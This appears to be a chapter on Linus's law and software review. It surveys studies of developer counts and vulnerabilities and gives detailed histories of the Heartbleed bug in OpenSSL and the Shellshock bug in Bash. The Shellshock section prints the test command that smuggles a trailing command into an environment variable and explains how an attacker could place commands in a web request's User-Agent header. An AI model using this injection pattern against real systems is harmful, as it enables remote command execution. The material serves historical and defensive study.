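Andrew Meneely and Laurie Williams tried to test the law with data in *Secure open source collaboration* (2009). They examined the kernel in Red Hat Enterprise Linux 4 and compared the number of developers who had changed each file with the vulnerabilities later found in it. Files changed by nine or more developers were 16 times as likely to have a known vulnerability as files changed by fewer. The researchers suggested there might be "too many cooks in the kitchen".

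*Investigating the Relationship between Developer Collaboration and Software Security* (Meneely, 2011) repeated the analysis with more vulnerabilities. Of the files that nine or more developers had changed, 44.4 per cent were vulnerable, compared with 2.9 per cent of the rest. But there were only about 60 such files out of more than 10,000, and auditing all of them would have covered only 9.5 per cent of the vulnerable files. Meneely and Williams found a similar pattern in the programming language PHP and in Wireshark, a tool for examining network traffic. In all three projects, files that six or more developers had changed were at least four times as likely to be vulnerable.

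The association between developers and vulnerabilities does not prove that extra developers cause them. Vulnerable files in the kernel received an average of 14.2 commits in the period studied, compared with 4.0 for other files. A file at the centre of the kernel may need many changes, attract many developers and contain many vulnerabilities because it does a lot of complicated work. Every change is also another opportunity to make a mistake, whoever makes it. The researchers counted only developers who had worked on a file before the release and only vulnerabilities discovered afterwards, so the people who fixed these vulnerabilities did not inflate the count.

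The study also counted only known vulnerabilities. If more people look at important files, they will find more of the vulnerabilities there, and those files will seem less secure than neglected ones. Linus's law would then predict the study's result. Meneely called files with no known vulnerabilities "neutral" instead of "safe" because nobody could tell how many undiscovered flaws they contained. The study also counted the people who changed a file, not those who checked it, so someone who only read the file and found nothing would not appear in the data.

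A later study of Chromium, the open-source basis of Google's Chrome browser, came closer to testing the claim by counting the people who had reviewed each file. Meneely and colleagues analysed 159,254 code reviews and 667 vulnerabilities that the reviews had missed. Files with more reviewers were again more likely to be vulnerable, even after the researchers allowed for file size. Projects may assign more reviewers to riskier code, so this does not show that extra reviewers do harm. But files were less likely to be vulnerable if their reviewers had previously helped review security fixes. The same group also found that the Chromium files with the most ordinary bugs for their size were not the ones with the most vulnerabilities for their size. Experience with security fixes might therefore matter because a reader who is good at finding one kind of bug may have had little practice with the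 other.

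## Heartbleed: two years in OpenSSL

Relatively few people depended on Mailman or Piranha, but much of the web uses the OpenSSL library for encryption. The project started in 1998 and its purpose is security, so its code seemed likely to attract careful readers. On 7 April 2014 the project published an advisory, OpenSSL (2014), about a missing bounds check that let anyone who connected to an affected server read up to 64 kilobytes of its memory. Codenomicon, a Finnish security firm that had also found the flaw, publicised it as Heartbleed.

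### The heartbeat message

A browser that opens an "https" address uses TLS, a protocol for encrypted connections. If a connection carries no data for a while, one side may need to check that the other is still there. *Transport Layer Security (TLS) and Datagram Transport Layer Security (DTLS) Heartbeat Extension* (Seggelmann, Tuexen and Williams, 2012) defines a message for this purpose, called a heartbeat. One side sends arbitrary data, and the other must return an exact copy.

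A heartbeat request has four parts:

- the type, one byte, which marks it as a request or a response
- the payload length, two bytes
- the payload, which is the data to send back
- the padding, at least 16 random bytes that the receiver ignores

The amount of padding can vary, so the receiver needs the length field to know where the payload ends. But the sender can set that field to any number up to 65,535, the largest that fits in two bytes. The receiver also knows how many bytes were in the record, the larger unit that carried the heartbeat, and that count is more reliable than the length field.

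Seggelmann and his co-authors foresaw that a heartbeat's stated payload length might not match its actual length, so their standard, RFC 6520, requires the receiver to discard any heartbeat whose stated length is too large. They also wrote in its security section that the document introduced no new security considerations.

### The missing check

The faulty code appears beside its replacement in the commit that fixed it, Henson's *Add heartbeat extension bounds check*. When a request arrived, the server did four things:

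1. It read the type and the stated payload length.
2. It reserved a buffer for the response, with room for the type, the length field, a payload of the stated length and 16 bytes of padding.
3. It copied the stated number of bytes into this buffer, starting at the first byte of the payload.
4. It added new padding and sent the response.

At no point did it compare the stated length with the number of bytes that had arrived.

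Suppose an honest client sends the payload "bird" and gives its length as 4. The message takes 1 + 2 + 4 + 16 = 23 bytes, and the server returns "bird". An attacker sends the same message but gives the length as 65,535. The server copies 65,535 bytes, of which the first 4 are "bird" and the next 16 are the attacker's own padding. The other 65,515 are whatever lies next in the server's memory.

The main part of the fix is one comparison. The server discards the message if

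1 + 2 + *stated payload length* + 16 > *record length*.

Both sides equal 23 for the honest request, so the server answers it. The attacker's request makes the left side 65,554 while the right side is still 23, so the server does nothing. A second check discards messages too short to hold even an empty payload. OpenSSL had one copy of the function for TLS and another for DTLS, a version of TLS for unreliable connections, and both needed the fix.

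An attacker could repeat the request to get more memory, 64 kilobytes at a time, according to US-CERT's *OpenSSL 'Heartbleed' vulnerability (CVE-2014-0160)*. That memory might include passwords or the server's private key, which an attacker could use to impersonate the site. The cryptographer Matthew Green wrote on the blog Cryptography Engineering that an attack left no trace.

### From New Year's Eve to disclosure

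Robin Seggelmann, the first author of the heartbeat standard, also wrote the code. He was a graduate student in Münster who contributed fixes and new features to OpenSSL as part of his research. Stephen Henson, the project's only full-time developer, reviewed the change and committed it on 31 December 2011. The log entry, Henson's *Support for TLS/DTLS heartbeats* (2011), lists Seggelmann as the submitter and "steve" as the reviewer. Its timestamp, about an hour before midnight in Britain, shows only when Henson stored the change, not when or how carefully he read it.

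On 27 February 2012, Henson committed another change by Seggelmann, *Fix padding bugs in Heartbeat support* (Henson, 2012). The length check was still missing when OpenSSL 1.0.1 came out on 14 March.

Neel Mehta of Google found the bug on 21 March 2014 while auditing the source code. Google patched its own servers that day and told the OpenSSL team on 1 April. Codenomicon found the bug independently on 2 April and reported it to Finland's national cyber security centre, which contacted OpenSSL on 7 April. Once the team knew that two groups had found the bug, it decided to release a corrected version the same day.

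*The Matter of Heartbleed*, by Durumeric, Kasten and colleagues, gives this sequence and describes how unevenly the news had spread. CloudFlare and Akamai, which deliver web pages for many other companies, knew in advance. Several makers of Linux systems had less than a day's notice, and other organizations, including Ubuntu and Cisco, had none.

From commit to fix, the vulnerability lasted about two years and three months. For nearly 25 of those months it was in released versions.

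### Exposure and repair

Durumeric and colleagues began scanning two days after disclosure, when many sites had already installed the fix, so they had to estimate how many had been exposed. Among the million most popular websites, 60 per cent of those offering HTTPS still supported heartbeats, and 91 per cent of these ran affected server software. If all of these had been vulnerable, about 55 per cent of the HTTPS sites were originally exposed. For a lower bound, the researchers counted only sites that ran affected server software and supported the newer TLS versions that OpenSSL had introduced alongside heartbeats, which gave about 24 per cent. At least 44 of the 100 most popular sites had been vulnerable.

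All of the top 100 sites had the fix within 48 hours, but smaller sites were slower. The vulnerable share of HTTPS sites in the top million fell from 11.5 per cent on 9 April to 3.1 per cent on 4 June, with little improvement after the first two weeks. Kudelski Security's *Heartbleed lets patch the internet* (2014) reports a separate scan of the whole internet, which found 1.76 million vulnerable servers on 10 April and 1.47 million three days later. The 10 April count was about 6 per cent of the servers that answered, close to the estimate by Durumeric and colleagues.

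Installing the fix did not protect a site if an attacker had already copied its private key. The owner also needed a new key and a new certificate, which certifies that the key belongs to the site. Of the popular sites that were still vulnerable two days after disclosure, 73 per cent installed the fix within a month but only 10 per cent replaced their certificates. Of the sites that replaced their certificates, 14 per cent kept the same private key, so the replacement did not protect them.

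Three weeks after disclosure, the researchers emailed the operators of the remaining vulnerable servers, starting with a randomly chosen half. Eight days later, 39.5 per cent of this half had begun patching, compared with 26.8 per cent of those not yet emailed. In a small follow-up survey, all 17 operators who replied already knew about Heartbleed, but several had missed some of their machines.

The researchers' own scanner had a bug too. It marked each server as safe by default, so a server whose test timed out stayed marked as safe. They estimated the resulting rate of missed servers at 6.5 to 10.5 per cent.

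How much harm attackers did is unclear. They used Heartbleed to break into the American hospital company Community Health Systems, in a breach that affected an estimated 4.5 million patients. But Bruce Schneier, who had called Heartbleed an 11 on a scale of 1 to 10, judged two months later that the damage had been minimal compared with the cost of restoring security (*The Human Side of Heartbleed*).

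### Why the reviewer missed it

Seggelmann told the *Sydney Morning Herald*, "I missed validating a variable containing a length" (reprinted in the Los Angeles Times, 2014). He denied that the mistake was deliberate. Deutsche Telekom, his later employer, published a statement from him without naming him, *Heartbleed developer talks about the error in OpenSSL programming*. In it, he said the reviewer had not noticed the mistake either.

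Someone who knew OpenSSL as well as anyone had reviewed the code, yet Durumeric and colleagues thought that a code review would probably have uncovered the vulnerability. They may have meant a more thorough review. David Wheeler, a specialist in secure software, makes this distinction in the most detailed study of how the bug escaped notice (Wheeler, 2014, *How to Prevent the next Heartbleed*). Someone reviewing a proposed change has to judge whether the feature works while also looking for vulnerabilities, which makes vulnerabilities easier to miss than in an audit devoted to finding them.

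The code also looked careful about lengths. A reviewer who worries about memory errors in C will often check whether the buffer is big enough for the data being copied into it. This buffer always was, because the server reserved exactly as much space as it was about to fill. The error was in reading the source, which could contain less data than the server tried to copy. To notice this, Henson had to remember that the length came from an untrusted sender and that the record contained a second length to compare it with.

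The code's variable names were confusing, with "payload" holding the payload's length and "pl" pointing to the payload itself. One reader of Green's blog post complained that such names make bugs like this hard to spot.

One reviewer missing the bug is not very surprising. In Basili and Selby's experiment, professionals reading short programs they knew to be faulty still missed about 40 per cent of the bugs. It is harder to explain why nothing else caught the bug for two years.

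### Why tests and tools missed it

Wheeler calls the usual test suite "mostly-positive" because it mainly checks that correct input gives correct output. Developers naturally test this way, since users complain when correct input fails and seldom try anything else. Connecting OpenSSL to other TLS programs would not have exposed the bug, because those programs also try to follow the standard and send correct lengths. Measuring how much of the code the tests ran would not have exposed it either, because that can reveal a line no test has reached, but the problem here was a missing line. Mike Bland wrote a test file for heartbeats on 12 April 2014, five days after disclosure, and Laurie's *Merge branch 'mbland-heartbeat-test-1.0.2' into OpenSSL_1_0_2-stable* added it to the library.

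Static analysis tools can consider many possible inputs at once, and several look specifically for reads past the end of a buffer. People routinely ran such tools on OpenSSL. But to flag this bug, a tool had to follow the length value from the network, through several layers of code, to the copying step. Most commercial tools take shortcuts to finish in a reasonable time and limit false alarms. Wheeler says that Coverity, GrammaTech's CodeSonar and Klocwork in its normal configuration would all have missed Heartbleed. CodeSonar did find it when GrammaTech switched on a slower analysis for the right section of code, but Wheeler doesn't count this because choosing that section required already knowing where the bug was.

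He knows of one exception. After disclosure, someone at a government laboratory reported that CQual++, a free research tool, had found Heartbleed when run in its standard configuration, while the commercial tools they tried had not. The person called the tool "a bit difficult to run and interpret", which may be why nobody had used it to find the bug earlier. The report is anonymous and second-hand, so it is weak evidence.

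Fuzzers could easily miss Heartbleed because most of them only watched for crashes, even though fuzzing seems well suited to a bug that depends on strange input. Writing past the end of a buffer often crashes a program, but reading past the end usually doesn't. A fuzzer could have sent the right message, received a piece of the server's memory in reply and recorded nothing unusual. Some fuzzers would not have sent the message at all. Sulley, a popular toolkit, by default recalculated each length field to match the data.

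### What could have caught it

Wheeler then listed methods that would certainly or very probably have caught Heartbleed in advance. The main ones are below, roughly from cheapest to most expensive, with the evidence for each.

| Method | What it involves | Evidence that it catches Heartbleed |
|---|---|---|
| Negative tests | Sending wrong values in every field and checking that the program rejects them | Wheeler's argument |
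| Fuzzing with an address checker | Making any read outside a buffer crash the program | Found it in a 2015 trial |
| A review checklist | Requiring the reviewer to confirm that the code validates every field from outside | Wheeler's argument |
| Fuzzing with checks on the output | Looking for replies that are too large or contain odd data | Codenomicon found it this way |
| Specially configured static analysis | Giving the tool more information about the program | Klocwork found it after disclosure |
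| A safer language | Using a language that checks bounds automatically | Follows from how such languages work |
| A security audit | Having experts search the code on the assumption that it is vulnerable | Mehta found it this way |
| Formal proof | Proving mathematically that the code meets its specification | Wheeler's argument |

Only Codenomicon's method and Mehta's audit found the bug when nobody knew it was there, but Hanno Böck's 2015 trial is also fairly persuasive. He combined a fuzzer called american fuzzy lop with AddressSanitizer, a checker that programmers can switch on when they compile a program. Together they found Heartbleed automatically in six hours on ordinary hardware. AddressSanitizer had been available since 2012, but Böck noted that the fuzzer was probably not ready to find the bug so easily in early 2014.

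The case for negative tests is strong, though it rests on argument. The standard has an explicit rule about lengths that are too large, so anyone writing a test for each rule would have tested for them without needing to suspect a bug or even read the code. Wheeler adds that people outside the development team can write such tests and that one set could serve every TLS library.

The checklist is less certain to work, since checklists made no clear difference in the 308 industrial inspections. Wheeler's item is much more specific than most, which should help, but the right item is easier to choose once the bug is known.

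Wheeler thinks well of audits and cites an experiment by James Kupsch and Barton Miller. On one sample program, human auditors found 15 serious vulnerabilities, while the static analysis tools Fortify and Coverity found 6 and 1, respectively, all of which the auditors had also found. The auditors did much better than the tools of the time, but the experiment doesn't show how many vulnerabilities all of them missed.

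### Who was working on OpenSSL

Besides Henson, the project's website listed three core volunteers. One of them, Ben Laurie, was a Google engineer who worked on OpenSSL on nights and weekends. The project received about $2,000 a year in donations, according to *Heartbleed highlights a contradiction in the web*, a *New York Times* article reprinted in Business Standard. After meeting Henson, who was working on OpenSSL full time and, in Marquess's word, "starving", Steve Marquess set up a foundation to find the programmers paid consulting work. The foundation never earned more than $1 million a year from these contracts, and clients mostly pay for the work they want, which may not include code review.

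*Free Can Make You Bleed* (jones_supa), a post on the technology site Slashdot, quotes an estimate that all this labour amounted to about two full-time developers for 500,000 lines of code. At the pace Fagan planned for operating-system code, a team of four would need more than three years to inspect that much once. About ten years before Heartbleed, Laurie spent a year auditing OpenSSL for the American defence research agency DARPA, but the heartbeat code did not exist then. By 2014 he said that volunteers no longer had time for such an audit.

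The code was also hard to read. The security researcher Dan Kaminsky (2014) wrote that OpenSSL was "legendary for being considered a mess, internally". It supported more than eighty platforms, some of them long obsolete, partly through nested instructions that included or excluded code for each one. Some of its functions had names similar to those of standard C functions but behaved differently.

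OpenSSL's handling of memory confused even specialists who were studying it closely. The library kept some released memory on a list for reuse instead of returning it to the system. Shortly after Heartbleed was disclosed, Kupsch and Miller reported that OpenSSL also split large blocks of memory into smaller ones, which would have hidden the bug from address checkers. Wheeler repeated the claim in early versions of his study. He and another researcher, Chris Rohlf, then each reread the code and concluded that it did not split blocks, and Kupsch and Miller corrected their paper. Wheeler took the episode as evidence that the memory code was too complex. It also suggests that a reader was less likely to notice a bug in OpenSSL than in a simpler program.

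### Two discoveries in twelve days

Nobody reported the bug for more than two years, and then Mehta and Codenomicon found it twelve days apart. Schneier called this "an odd coincidence", and some people suspected that one team had heard about the other's discovery.

Mehta found the bug by reading the code. Codenomicon found it while testing Safeguard, a new feature of its fuzzer that examined a program's replies instead of waiting for a crash. A Codenomicon engineer had thought of the feature after studying an earlier vulnerability that could make a program skip a stage of logging in. Safeguard compared the size of each reply with the size of the request and, if the reply was suspiciously large, looked for signs of leaked data. Codenomicon built these checks for TLS first, and Heartbleed triggered both.

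Codenomicon found the bug when it did because it had built a tool that could detect it. Why Mehta was reading the same library that month is more a matter of guesswork. A serious flaw in Apple's TLS code had become public earlier in 2014, which may have led researchers to examine similar libraries.

The short interval between the two discoveries is less surprising than it seems, because OpenSSL announced the bug on 7 April, 17 days after Mehta found it, and nobody could discover it independently after that. It is more surprising that there was a second discovery at all. If another team was bound to find the bug between its release and its disclosure, and every day was equally likely, the chance of this happening in the last 17 days was about 2 per cent. That is small, but people remember Heartbleed's double discovery because it was unusual, and they don't count all the vulnerabilities that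 only one team found.

Durumeric and colleagues describe Codenomicon's discovery as independent, and Safeguard is enough to explain how it happened. A leak is also possible, since CloudFlare knew about the bug by 31 March, two days before Codenomicon found it, and Durumeric and colleagues write that the news spread privately among insiders.

Somebody may also have found the bug earlier and kept quiet. Durumeric and colleagues searched network traffic recorded before disclosure at three research institutions and a decoy server, and found no attacks. The recordings covered only parts of the two years, including February and March of 2012 and 2013 at one laboratory. Their result makes widespread scanning in those periods unlikely but can't rule out a few targeted attacks. Schneier was sure that the US National Security Agency had advance warning, and the US government denied any prior knowledge,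 but neither offered conclusive evidence.

### Was anyone looking?

Many commentators thought Heartbleed undermined Linus's law. Datamation's *Does Heartbleed Disprove Open Source Is Safer* observed that such bugs were not supposed to happen in public code that people worked with every day. Coding Horror's *Given Enough Money, All Bugs Are Shallow* called it "a turning point for Linus's Law", but accepted that public code probably gets more review than code only ten employees can see.

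Raymond replied that in this case "there weren't any eyeballs". He argued that companies built OpenSSL into their products but did not profit directly from maintaining it, so they left the work to people who weren't paid to do it. Meshed Insights' *Heartbleed and Lessons Learned* (2014) defends Linus's law on similar grounds, arguing that many people have to inspect the code and understand what they see, and that an open-source licence guarantees neither.

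Ten people reading the code carefully and independently, each with a 30 per cent chance of noticing the missing check, would almost certainly have caught it between them. So either fewer than about ten people read those lines carefully in two years, or each reader's chance of noticing the bug was much lower than 30 per cent.

The known facts about OpenSSL's staff support the first explanation. Schneier also wrote that nobody took the time to review the code after its release. He can't have known this for certain, and engineers at Google and Cisco had reported other OpenSSL bugs over the years, but nothing suggests that dozens of people had studied the heartbeat function. The bug was of a well-known type and took a few lines to fix, and a skilled auditor found it by reading the code. This suggests the bug was fairly easy to find for someone with the right training who was looking for it, though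 the state of the code made it harder.

Raymond's reply is therefore probably right about Heartbleed, but it makes the law of little practical use to someone deciding whether to trust a program. OpenSSL was public, important and very widely used, yet it still lacked the readers that the law requires. As the computer scientist Steven Bellovin put it, "Everybody's job is not anybody's job." OpenSSL's many users could not make up for the lack of readers, because the bug caused no symptoms in ordinary use.

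### What changed at OpenSSL

In the week or so after disclosure, OpenSSL received $17,000 in donations, almost entirely from individuals. The Linux Foundation then set up the Core Infrastructure Initiative to pay for neglected open-source projects that many companies relied on. According to a news report that a reader posted under Schneier's essay, 17 companies each pledged $100,000 a year for at least three years, to be shared among OpenSSL and two other projects. The first $1.7 million allowed Henson and another developer, Andy Polyakov, to work on OpenSSL full time. The initiative also agreed to fund an outside audit.

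Developers of the operating system OpenBSD made their own version of OpenSSL, called LibreSSL, and began to remove old code and reformat the rest to make it readable. Wheeler approved of most of this but noted that they were also removing features that some users needed, including support for a certification that the US government requires.

In June 2015, someone asked whether heartbeats had any valid use, and an OpenSSL developer replied that he couldn't see one for TLS, the protocol that secures ordinary web connections (Salz, 2015, *Patch fixing some heartbeat issues (vs latest git master)*). The project later removed heartbeats from TLS and disabled them by default in DTLS (Salz, *Remove TLS heartbeat, disable DTLS heartbeat*). The log entry for that commit names a second developer as reviewer, as did the entry for the New Year's Eve 2011 commit.

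Wheeler writes that OpenSSL improved after the new money arrived. The improvements did not include a complete search of the old code. The small memory error in the DES cipher that FuzzingBrain found after 25 years was already in the library when Mehta began reading, and AI systems have since found other old flaws there.

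## Shellshock: twenty-five years in Bash

A skilled reader found Heartbleed, a missing comparison in one function, by reading the code. Shellshock was in the command interpreter Bash from August 1989 to September 2014, about eleven times as long as Heartbleed lasted, and the person who discovered it had not been reading the code.

### Shells, variables and functions

A shell is a program that carries out commands. When a user types `date`, the shell starts the `date` program, which prints the date. A file of such commands is a script. Other programs also start a shell when they need to run something, so a shell may be running on a server where nobody is typing. Brian Fox began writing Bash in late 1987 for the GNU Project, which was building a free operating system. By 2014 Red Hat's Linux and several others used Bash to run their scripts.

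An environment variable is a named piece of text that a program passes to the programs it starts, called its child processes. For example, `HOME=/home/alice` gives the location of Alice's files. Each child normally receives a copy of all the parent's variables and ignores most of them.

Bash users can also define functions, which are named groups of commands. After `greet() { echo hello; }`, typing `greet` runs `echo hello`, which prints "hello". A second Bash shell started from the first would not normally have `greet`, so in 1989 Fox added a way to pass functions on. The first shell stored the function as an environment variable, `greet=() { echo hello; }`. When the second shell started, it searched all its variables for values beginning with `() {`. According to *Shellshock timeline* (Chazelas, 2014), a mailing-list thread about the bug's history, Bash then simply replaced the equals sign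 with a space and interpreted the result, `greet () { echo hello; }`, as if somebody had typed it.

But Bash interpreted the whole value, including anything after the function. A semicolon separates commands, so if the value was `() { echo hello; }; date`, the second shell defined the function and then ran `date`. Bash never wrote such a value itself, because it stopped at the closing brace when it exported a function. Bachmeyer (2025), in *How to do secure coding and create secure software*, says the flaw went unnoticed for years because normal use never exercised the faulty path.

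### The test line

When the flaw became public, many people checked their machines with a harmless command:

`env x='() { :;}; echo vulnerable' bash -c "echo this is a test"`

It has five parts:

- `env` starts a program with an extra environment variable.
- `x='...'` names that variable and gives its value. The quotation marks make the current shell treat everything between them as plain text.
- `() { :;}` looks like an exported function. The colon is a command that does nothing.
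- `; echo vulnerable` is the trailing command, which should never run.
- `bash -c "echo this is a test"` starts a new Bash shell and gives it one command. The shell has to be new because, as InfoQ (2014) explains, Bash imports functions only when it starts.

A repaired Bash prints "this is a test", but a vulnerable one prints "vulnerable" first, even though the command it received doesn't use `x`. An attacker would replace `echo vulnerable` with something harmful.

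### Why a reader in 1989 had little reason to object

Running the trailing text was a mistake even in 1989, since importing a function should only define it. But the mistake was harmless because the variables came from the user's own session, and a user who wanted to run `date` could type it. Anyone who could set another person's variables already had easier ways to do damage. For instance, the variable `PATH` lists the folders where the shell looks for programs, so an attacker who controls it can substitute a false `date` for the real one. Programmers knew that the environment was dangerous for programs that run with more privileges than the user who starts them, and Bash came to ignore exported functions in that situation.

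Fox also discussed the feature openly. A week after the release, Breuel (1989), in *exportable functions*, asked a public newsgroup for functions that could be passed between shells, as they could in an existing Unix shell. Fox replied the same day with the exact rule Bash used to recognise a function. Chet Ramey, who later became Bash's maintainer, posted a worked example.

Ramey also explained why Bash did not copy the older shell, which stored a function as `name(){value}`, without an equals sign. Other programs would have misread such entries, and Ramey called Bash's version "a nice compromise". The choice was sensible for compatibility, the only consideration anyone raised in the thread. However, it meant that Bash recognised a function by the variable's value instead of the form of its name, which made no difference to security while the same person chose both.

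Some years later, web servers began storing text from strangers in environment variables. Under a convention called CGI, a server answers a request by starting a program and passing it the details in variables that the server names. For example, a browser usually sends a line identifying itself, which the server stores as `HTTP_USER_AGENT`. The sender can write anything there, including `() { :;};` followed by a command. If the program is a Bash script, or starts Bash for any other reason, the new shell searches its variables, finds the four characters `() {` and runs the command.

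Weimer (2014) described this route in *CVE-2014-6271*, a notice for companies that could filter attacks on their networks. *Bash gets shellshocked* (Edge, 2014) lists several others, including mail servers, restricted logins over SSH (the usual way to log in to a remote machine) and the programs that set up a computer's network connection. Debian and Ubuntu were less exposed because they had switched most scripts to a smaller shell, mainly for speed.

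Someone reading the web server's code would have had no more reason to object than someone reading Bash's. Programs had always used environment variables to carry data, and shells have no use for one called `HTTP_USER_AGENT`. Weimer (2014), in *Thoughts on Shellshock and beyond*, suggested that people might have called the problem a bug in CGI if somebody had noticed it when the first CGI server appeared. Wheeler (2025), in *Shellshock*, agrees with another security specialist that the CVEs rightly named Bash. That view seems better because strangers could reach Bash by so many routes that fixing each one separately would have been hopeless.

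The bug became a vulnerability because of CGI servers, not because of any change to Bash. A reviewer who read every later commit to Bash would not have seen this happen, and a reviewer of the first CGI server would have seen only code that stored text in environment variables. The bug's twenty-five-year lifetime therefore includes some early years when it posed little danger.

### People who came close

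At least twice, people outside the project examined the import mechanism without finding the flaw. In November 2001, Schaefer, a developer of the rival shell zsh, tried three slightly different values and found that Bash created a function only if the first four characters were `() {` (*export -f problem*, 2001). One malformed value produced a syntax error from Bash, a sign that it was interpreting the text as commands. Schaefer called the rule "rather horrible" and then considered which functions zsh should refuse to import. The message includes no test with a command after the closing brace.

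The second case, in November 2004, concerned sudo, a program that lets chosen users run chosen commands with an administrator's privileges. Liam Helmer noticed that sudo passed exported functions to the scripts it ran. If a script used the command `ifconfig`, a user could export a function of that name, and the script would run the function with an administrator's privileges. Sudo's developers fixed this and published an advisory explaining that Bash turns any variable whose value begins with "()" into a function.

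Linux distributors disagreed about whether it mattered. Jeppesen (2004), in *app-admin/sudo exported bash functions carried through sudo*, passed Helmer's report to the developers of Gentoo Linux. One of them, Tavis Ormandy, doubted that it was a security bug, since the same user could do the same thing by changing `PATH`. Debian issued an advisory, but Red Hat closed a similar report without a fix, partly because sudo is meant for trusted users (Novy, 2004, *CVE-2004-1051 bash scripts run via Sudo can be subverted*).

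Ormandy's argument was reasonable for sudo, whose users already had accounts on the machine and could choose the names of their variables. But nobody in these discussions asked what Bash did with text that followed a function definition, or whether a stranger might control a variable's value without controlling its name. By 2014, sudo discarded variables whose values began with "()", so attackers could not exploit Shellshock through sudo, but web servers had no such filter.

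### The discovery

Stéphane Chazelas had known about exported functions for some time. In July 2014 he found a vulnerability in the GNU C library, which most Linux programs use. It also involved environment variables, and an attacker could exploit it through restricted SSH log-ins. When Wheeler later asked how this had led to Shellshock, Chazelas replied that he had considered what exported functions would do in the same setting (Chazelas, 2014, *Stéphane Chazelas*). He thought about how someone might have written the import code and realised that the simplest way would leave a big security hole. He did not find the bug by looking at Bash's code. He had no reason to believe that anyone had exploited it earlier, though he couldn't rule it out.

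Chazelas discovered the bug on the morning of 12 September and wrote that afternoon to Ramey and the security contacts of four Linux distributors. Ramey produced a patch the same day, but it was easy to bypass, and the group went through several more versions. By 16 September, Ramey had patches for every version of Bash back to 3.0. The group planned to announce the flaw at 14:00 UTC on 24 September, and Weimer announced it about five minutes late. He published the technical details an hour later because somebody had leaked most of them to the press.

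*Shellshock* (Wheeler, 2014) reports that attackers soon used the flaw to build a botnet, a network of hijacked machines, which scanned and attacked systems at the US Department of Defense and Akamai. The flaw was easier to exploit than Heartbleed, and it let attackers run commands on a machine rather than only leaking its memory.

### Dating the bug

The first published dates were wrong by three or four years. Ramey told Chazelas and news outlets that the feature had arrived in version 1.13, around 1993, and Edge's article dates it to about 1992. On 3 October, Eric Kobrin of Akamai reported finding the vulnerable code in an archive of version 1.05, apparently from 1989 or 1990. Chazelas replied that the feature was "definitely not in 1.05 nor 1.12".

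Fifteen minutes later, Chazelas withdrew this. He had found a copy of version 1.12 that contained the feature, and the change log distributed with version 1.05 had an entry by Fox for 5 August 1989, "Added exporting of functions". Another entry recorded the release of version 1.03 on 1 September. Chazelas wrote that he and Ramey had "spread misconceptions".

Other volunteers tested old copies of the program. In *Shellshock timeline*, Riot (2014) describes running a 1991 version on an Atari system image and version 1.05 on an image for a Japanese computer, and both were vulnerable. Kobrin then found the September 1989 newsgroup thread in which Ramey had explained the feature. Ramey and Chazelas probably knew more about this bug than anyone else, yet both misremembered its age until others found the written records.

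### The incomplete patch

The patch released on 24 September made Bash stop after one command when it imported a function, according to the change log in GNU Bash's *commit bash-20141003 snapshot* (2014). So the trailing command in the test line no longer ran. But Bash still passed every value beginning with `() {` to its parser, the part of the program that works out the structure of commands. Strangers could therefore still send it text, and any bug in the parser might let them do harm.

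Weimer warned of this two and a half hours after the announcement. About seven hours after it, Ormandy, by then at Google, showed that a malformed function could still confuse the parser, making Bash misread the next command and create a file. Zalewski (2014) wrote in *CVE-2014-6271* that he and Ormandy had not found a more immediate danger in the example, but that it strongly suggested the parser was fragile.

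More flaws followed. The CVE team's reply in *Non-upstream patches for bash* (2014) assigned numbers to two memory errors. Zalewski (2014), in *the other bash RCEs (CVE-2014-6277 and CVE-2014-6278)*, credits these to Florian Weimer and Todd Sabin and gives the details of two more that he had found himself. In all, Shellshock received six CVEs:

| CVE | Finder | Made public in 2014 | Flaw |
|---|---|---|---|
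| CVE-2014-6271 | Chazelas | 24 September | Bash ran commands placed after a function |
| CVE-2014-7169 | Ormandy | 24 September | A malformed function made Bash misread the next command |
| CVE-2014-7186 and CVE-2014-7187 | Weimer and Sabin | By 26 September | Two memory errors, one in handling blocks of input text and one in deeply nested loops |
| CVE-2014-6277 | Zalewski | 1 October | Bash used a memory address that it had never set |
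| CVE-2014-6278 | Zalewski | 1 October | A different malformed function again let a stranger run any command |

Ramey's second patch, on 26 September, fixed only the flaw Ormandy had found. That day, Wheeler complained that repairing the parser one bug at a time was "whack-a-mole", because nobody had designed it to withstand attack and it was certain to contain many more bugs.

Weimer had already posted a better solution on 25 September, building on suggestions by Zalewski and Eric Blake. Under his patch, Bash imported a function only if the variable's name had a special beginning and ending. Red Hat and other distributors adopted it without waiting for the official version, which Ramey released on 27 September, three and a half days after the announcement. In that version, Bash exports the function `greet` in a variable called `BASH_FUNC_greet%%`. A web server stores a visitor's text under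 names such as `HTTP_USER_AGENT`, so Bash no longer parses it. The name now identifies the function, as it did in the older shell that Ramey had discussed in 1989. NetBSD and FreeBSD, two other free operating systems, went further and turned off automatic imports.

This ended the series without correcting the parser. Strangers could no longer reach the remaining bugs by this route, and Ramey fixed the known ones in three further patches by 5 October. The original test checks only whether trailing commands run, so it would pass a machine that had only the first patch. Its replacement, `env foo='() { echo not patched; }' bash -c foo`, checks whether Bash treats an ordinary variable as a function at all.

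Several experts had twelve days between the bug's discovery and its announcement to think about the first patch. In *Thoughts on Shellshock and beyond*, Zalewski (2014) argues that none of them immediately realised how complex the parser was, or that close inspection would probably reveal more bugs in it. This may be too harsh, because Chazelas recalls that the group did discuss whether to make Bash more resistant to attack in general. They nevertheless released a patch for the particular attack they had been shown.

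### What directed attention found

In twenty-five years, nobody publicly reported a vulnerability in the import code. In the week after the announcement, researchers published five more in the parser behind it. Zalewski found two of these with american fuzzy lop, the fuzzer that Böck later used to find Heartbleed. He gave it a small, valid function as a starting point and ran it for a couple of hours on one processor core. It also found three of the four flaws others had already reported.

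The contrast exaggerates how much attention alone achieved. Zalewski's fuzzer was new, so nobody could have used it for most of those twenty-five years. He thought that one of the two flaws he found might have entered the code only a few years earlier. Before Chazelas's discovery, people would also have considered a parser crash on a malformed function an ordinary bug, so some may have seen such crashes and never thought to report a vulnerability.

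Hardly anyone with a security background had looked at the code, for understandable reasons. Zalewski (2014) wrote in *Healing the bash fork* that the people who knew about exported functions and the people who knew about security had apparently not overlapped for a very long time. Zalewski had written many Bash scripts without knowing the feature existed, and so had Wheeler, who had used the shell daily since around 1995. Auditing Bash would also have seemed a poor use of time. By Wheeler's count, version 4.3 had 115,715 lines of code, which would take a team of four about 193 working days to inspect at the pace Fagan planned for operating-system code.

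Fox told *Wired* that going so long without a bug of this kind was "a pretty impressive ratio of usage to bugs found". But only text that Bash never wrote could trigger this bug, so even very heavy use was unlikely to do so.

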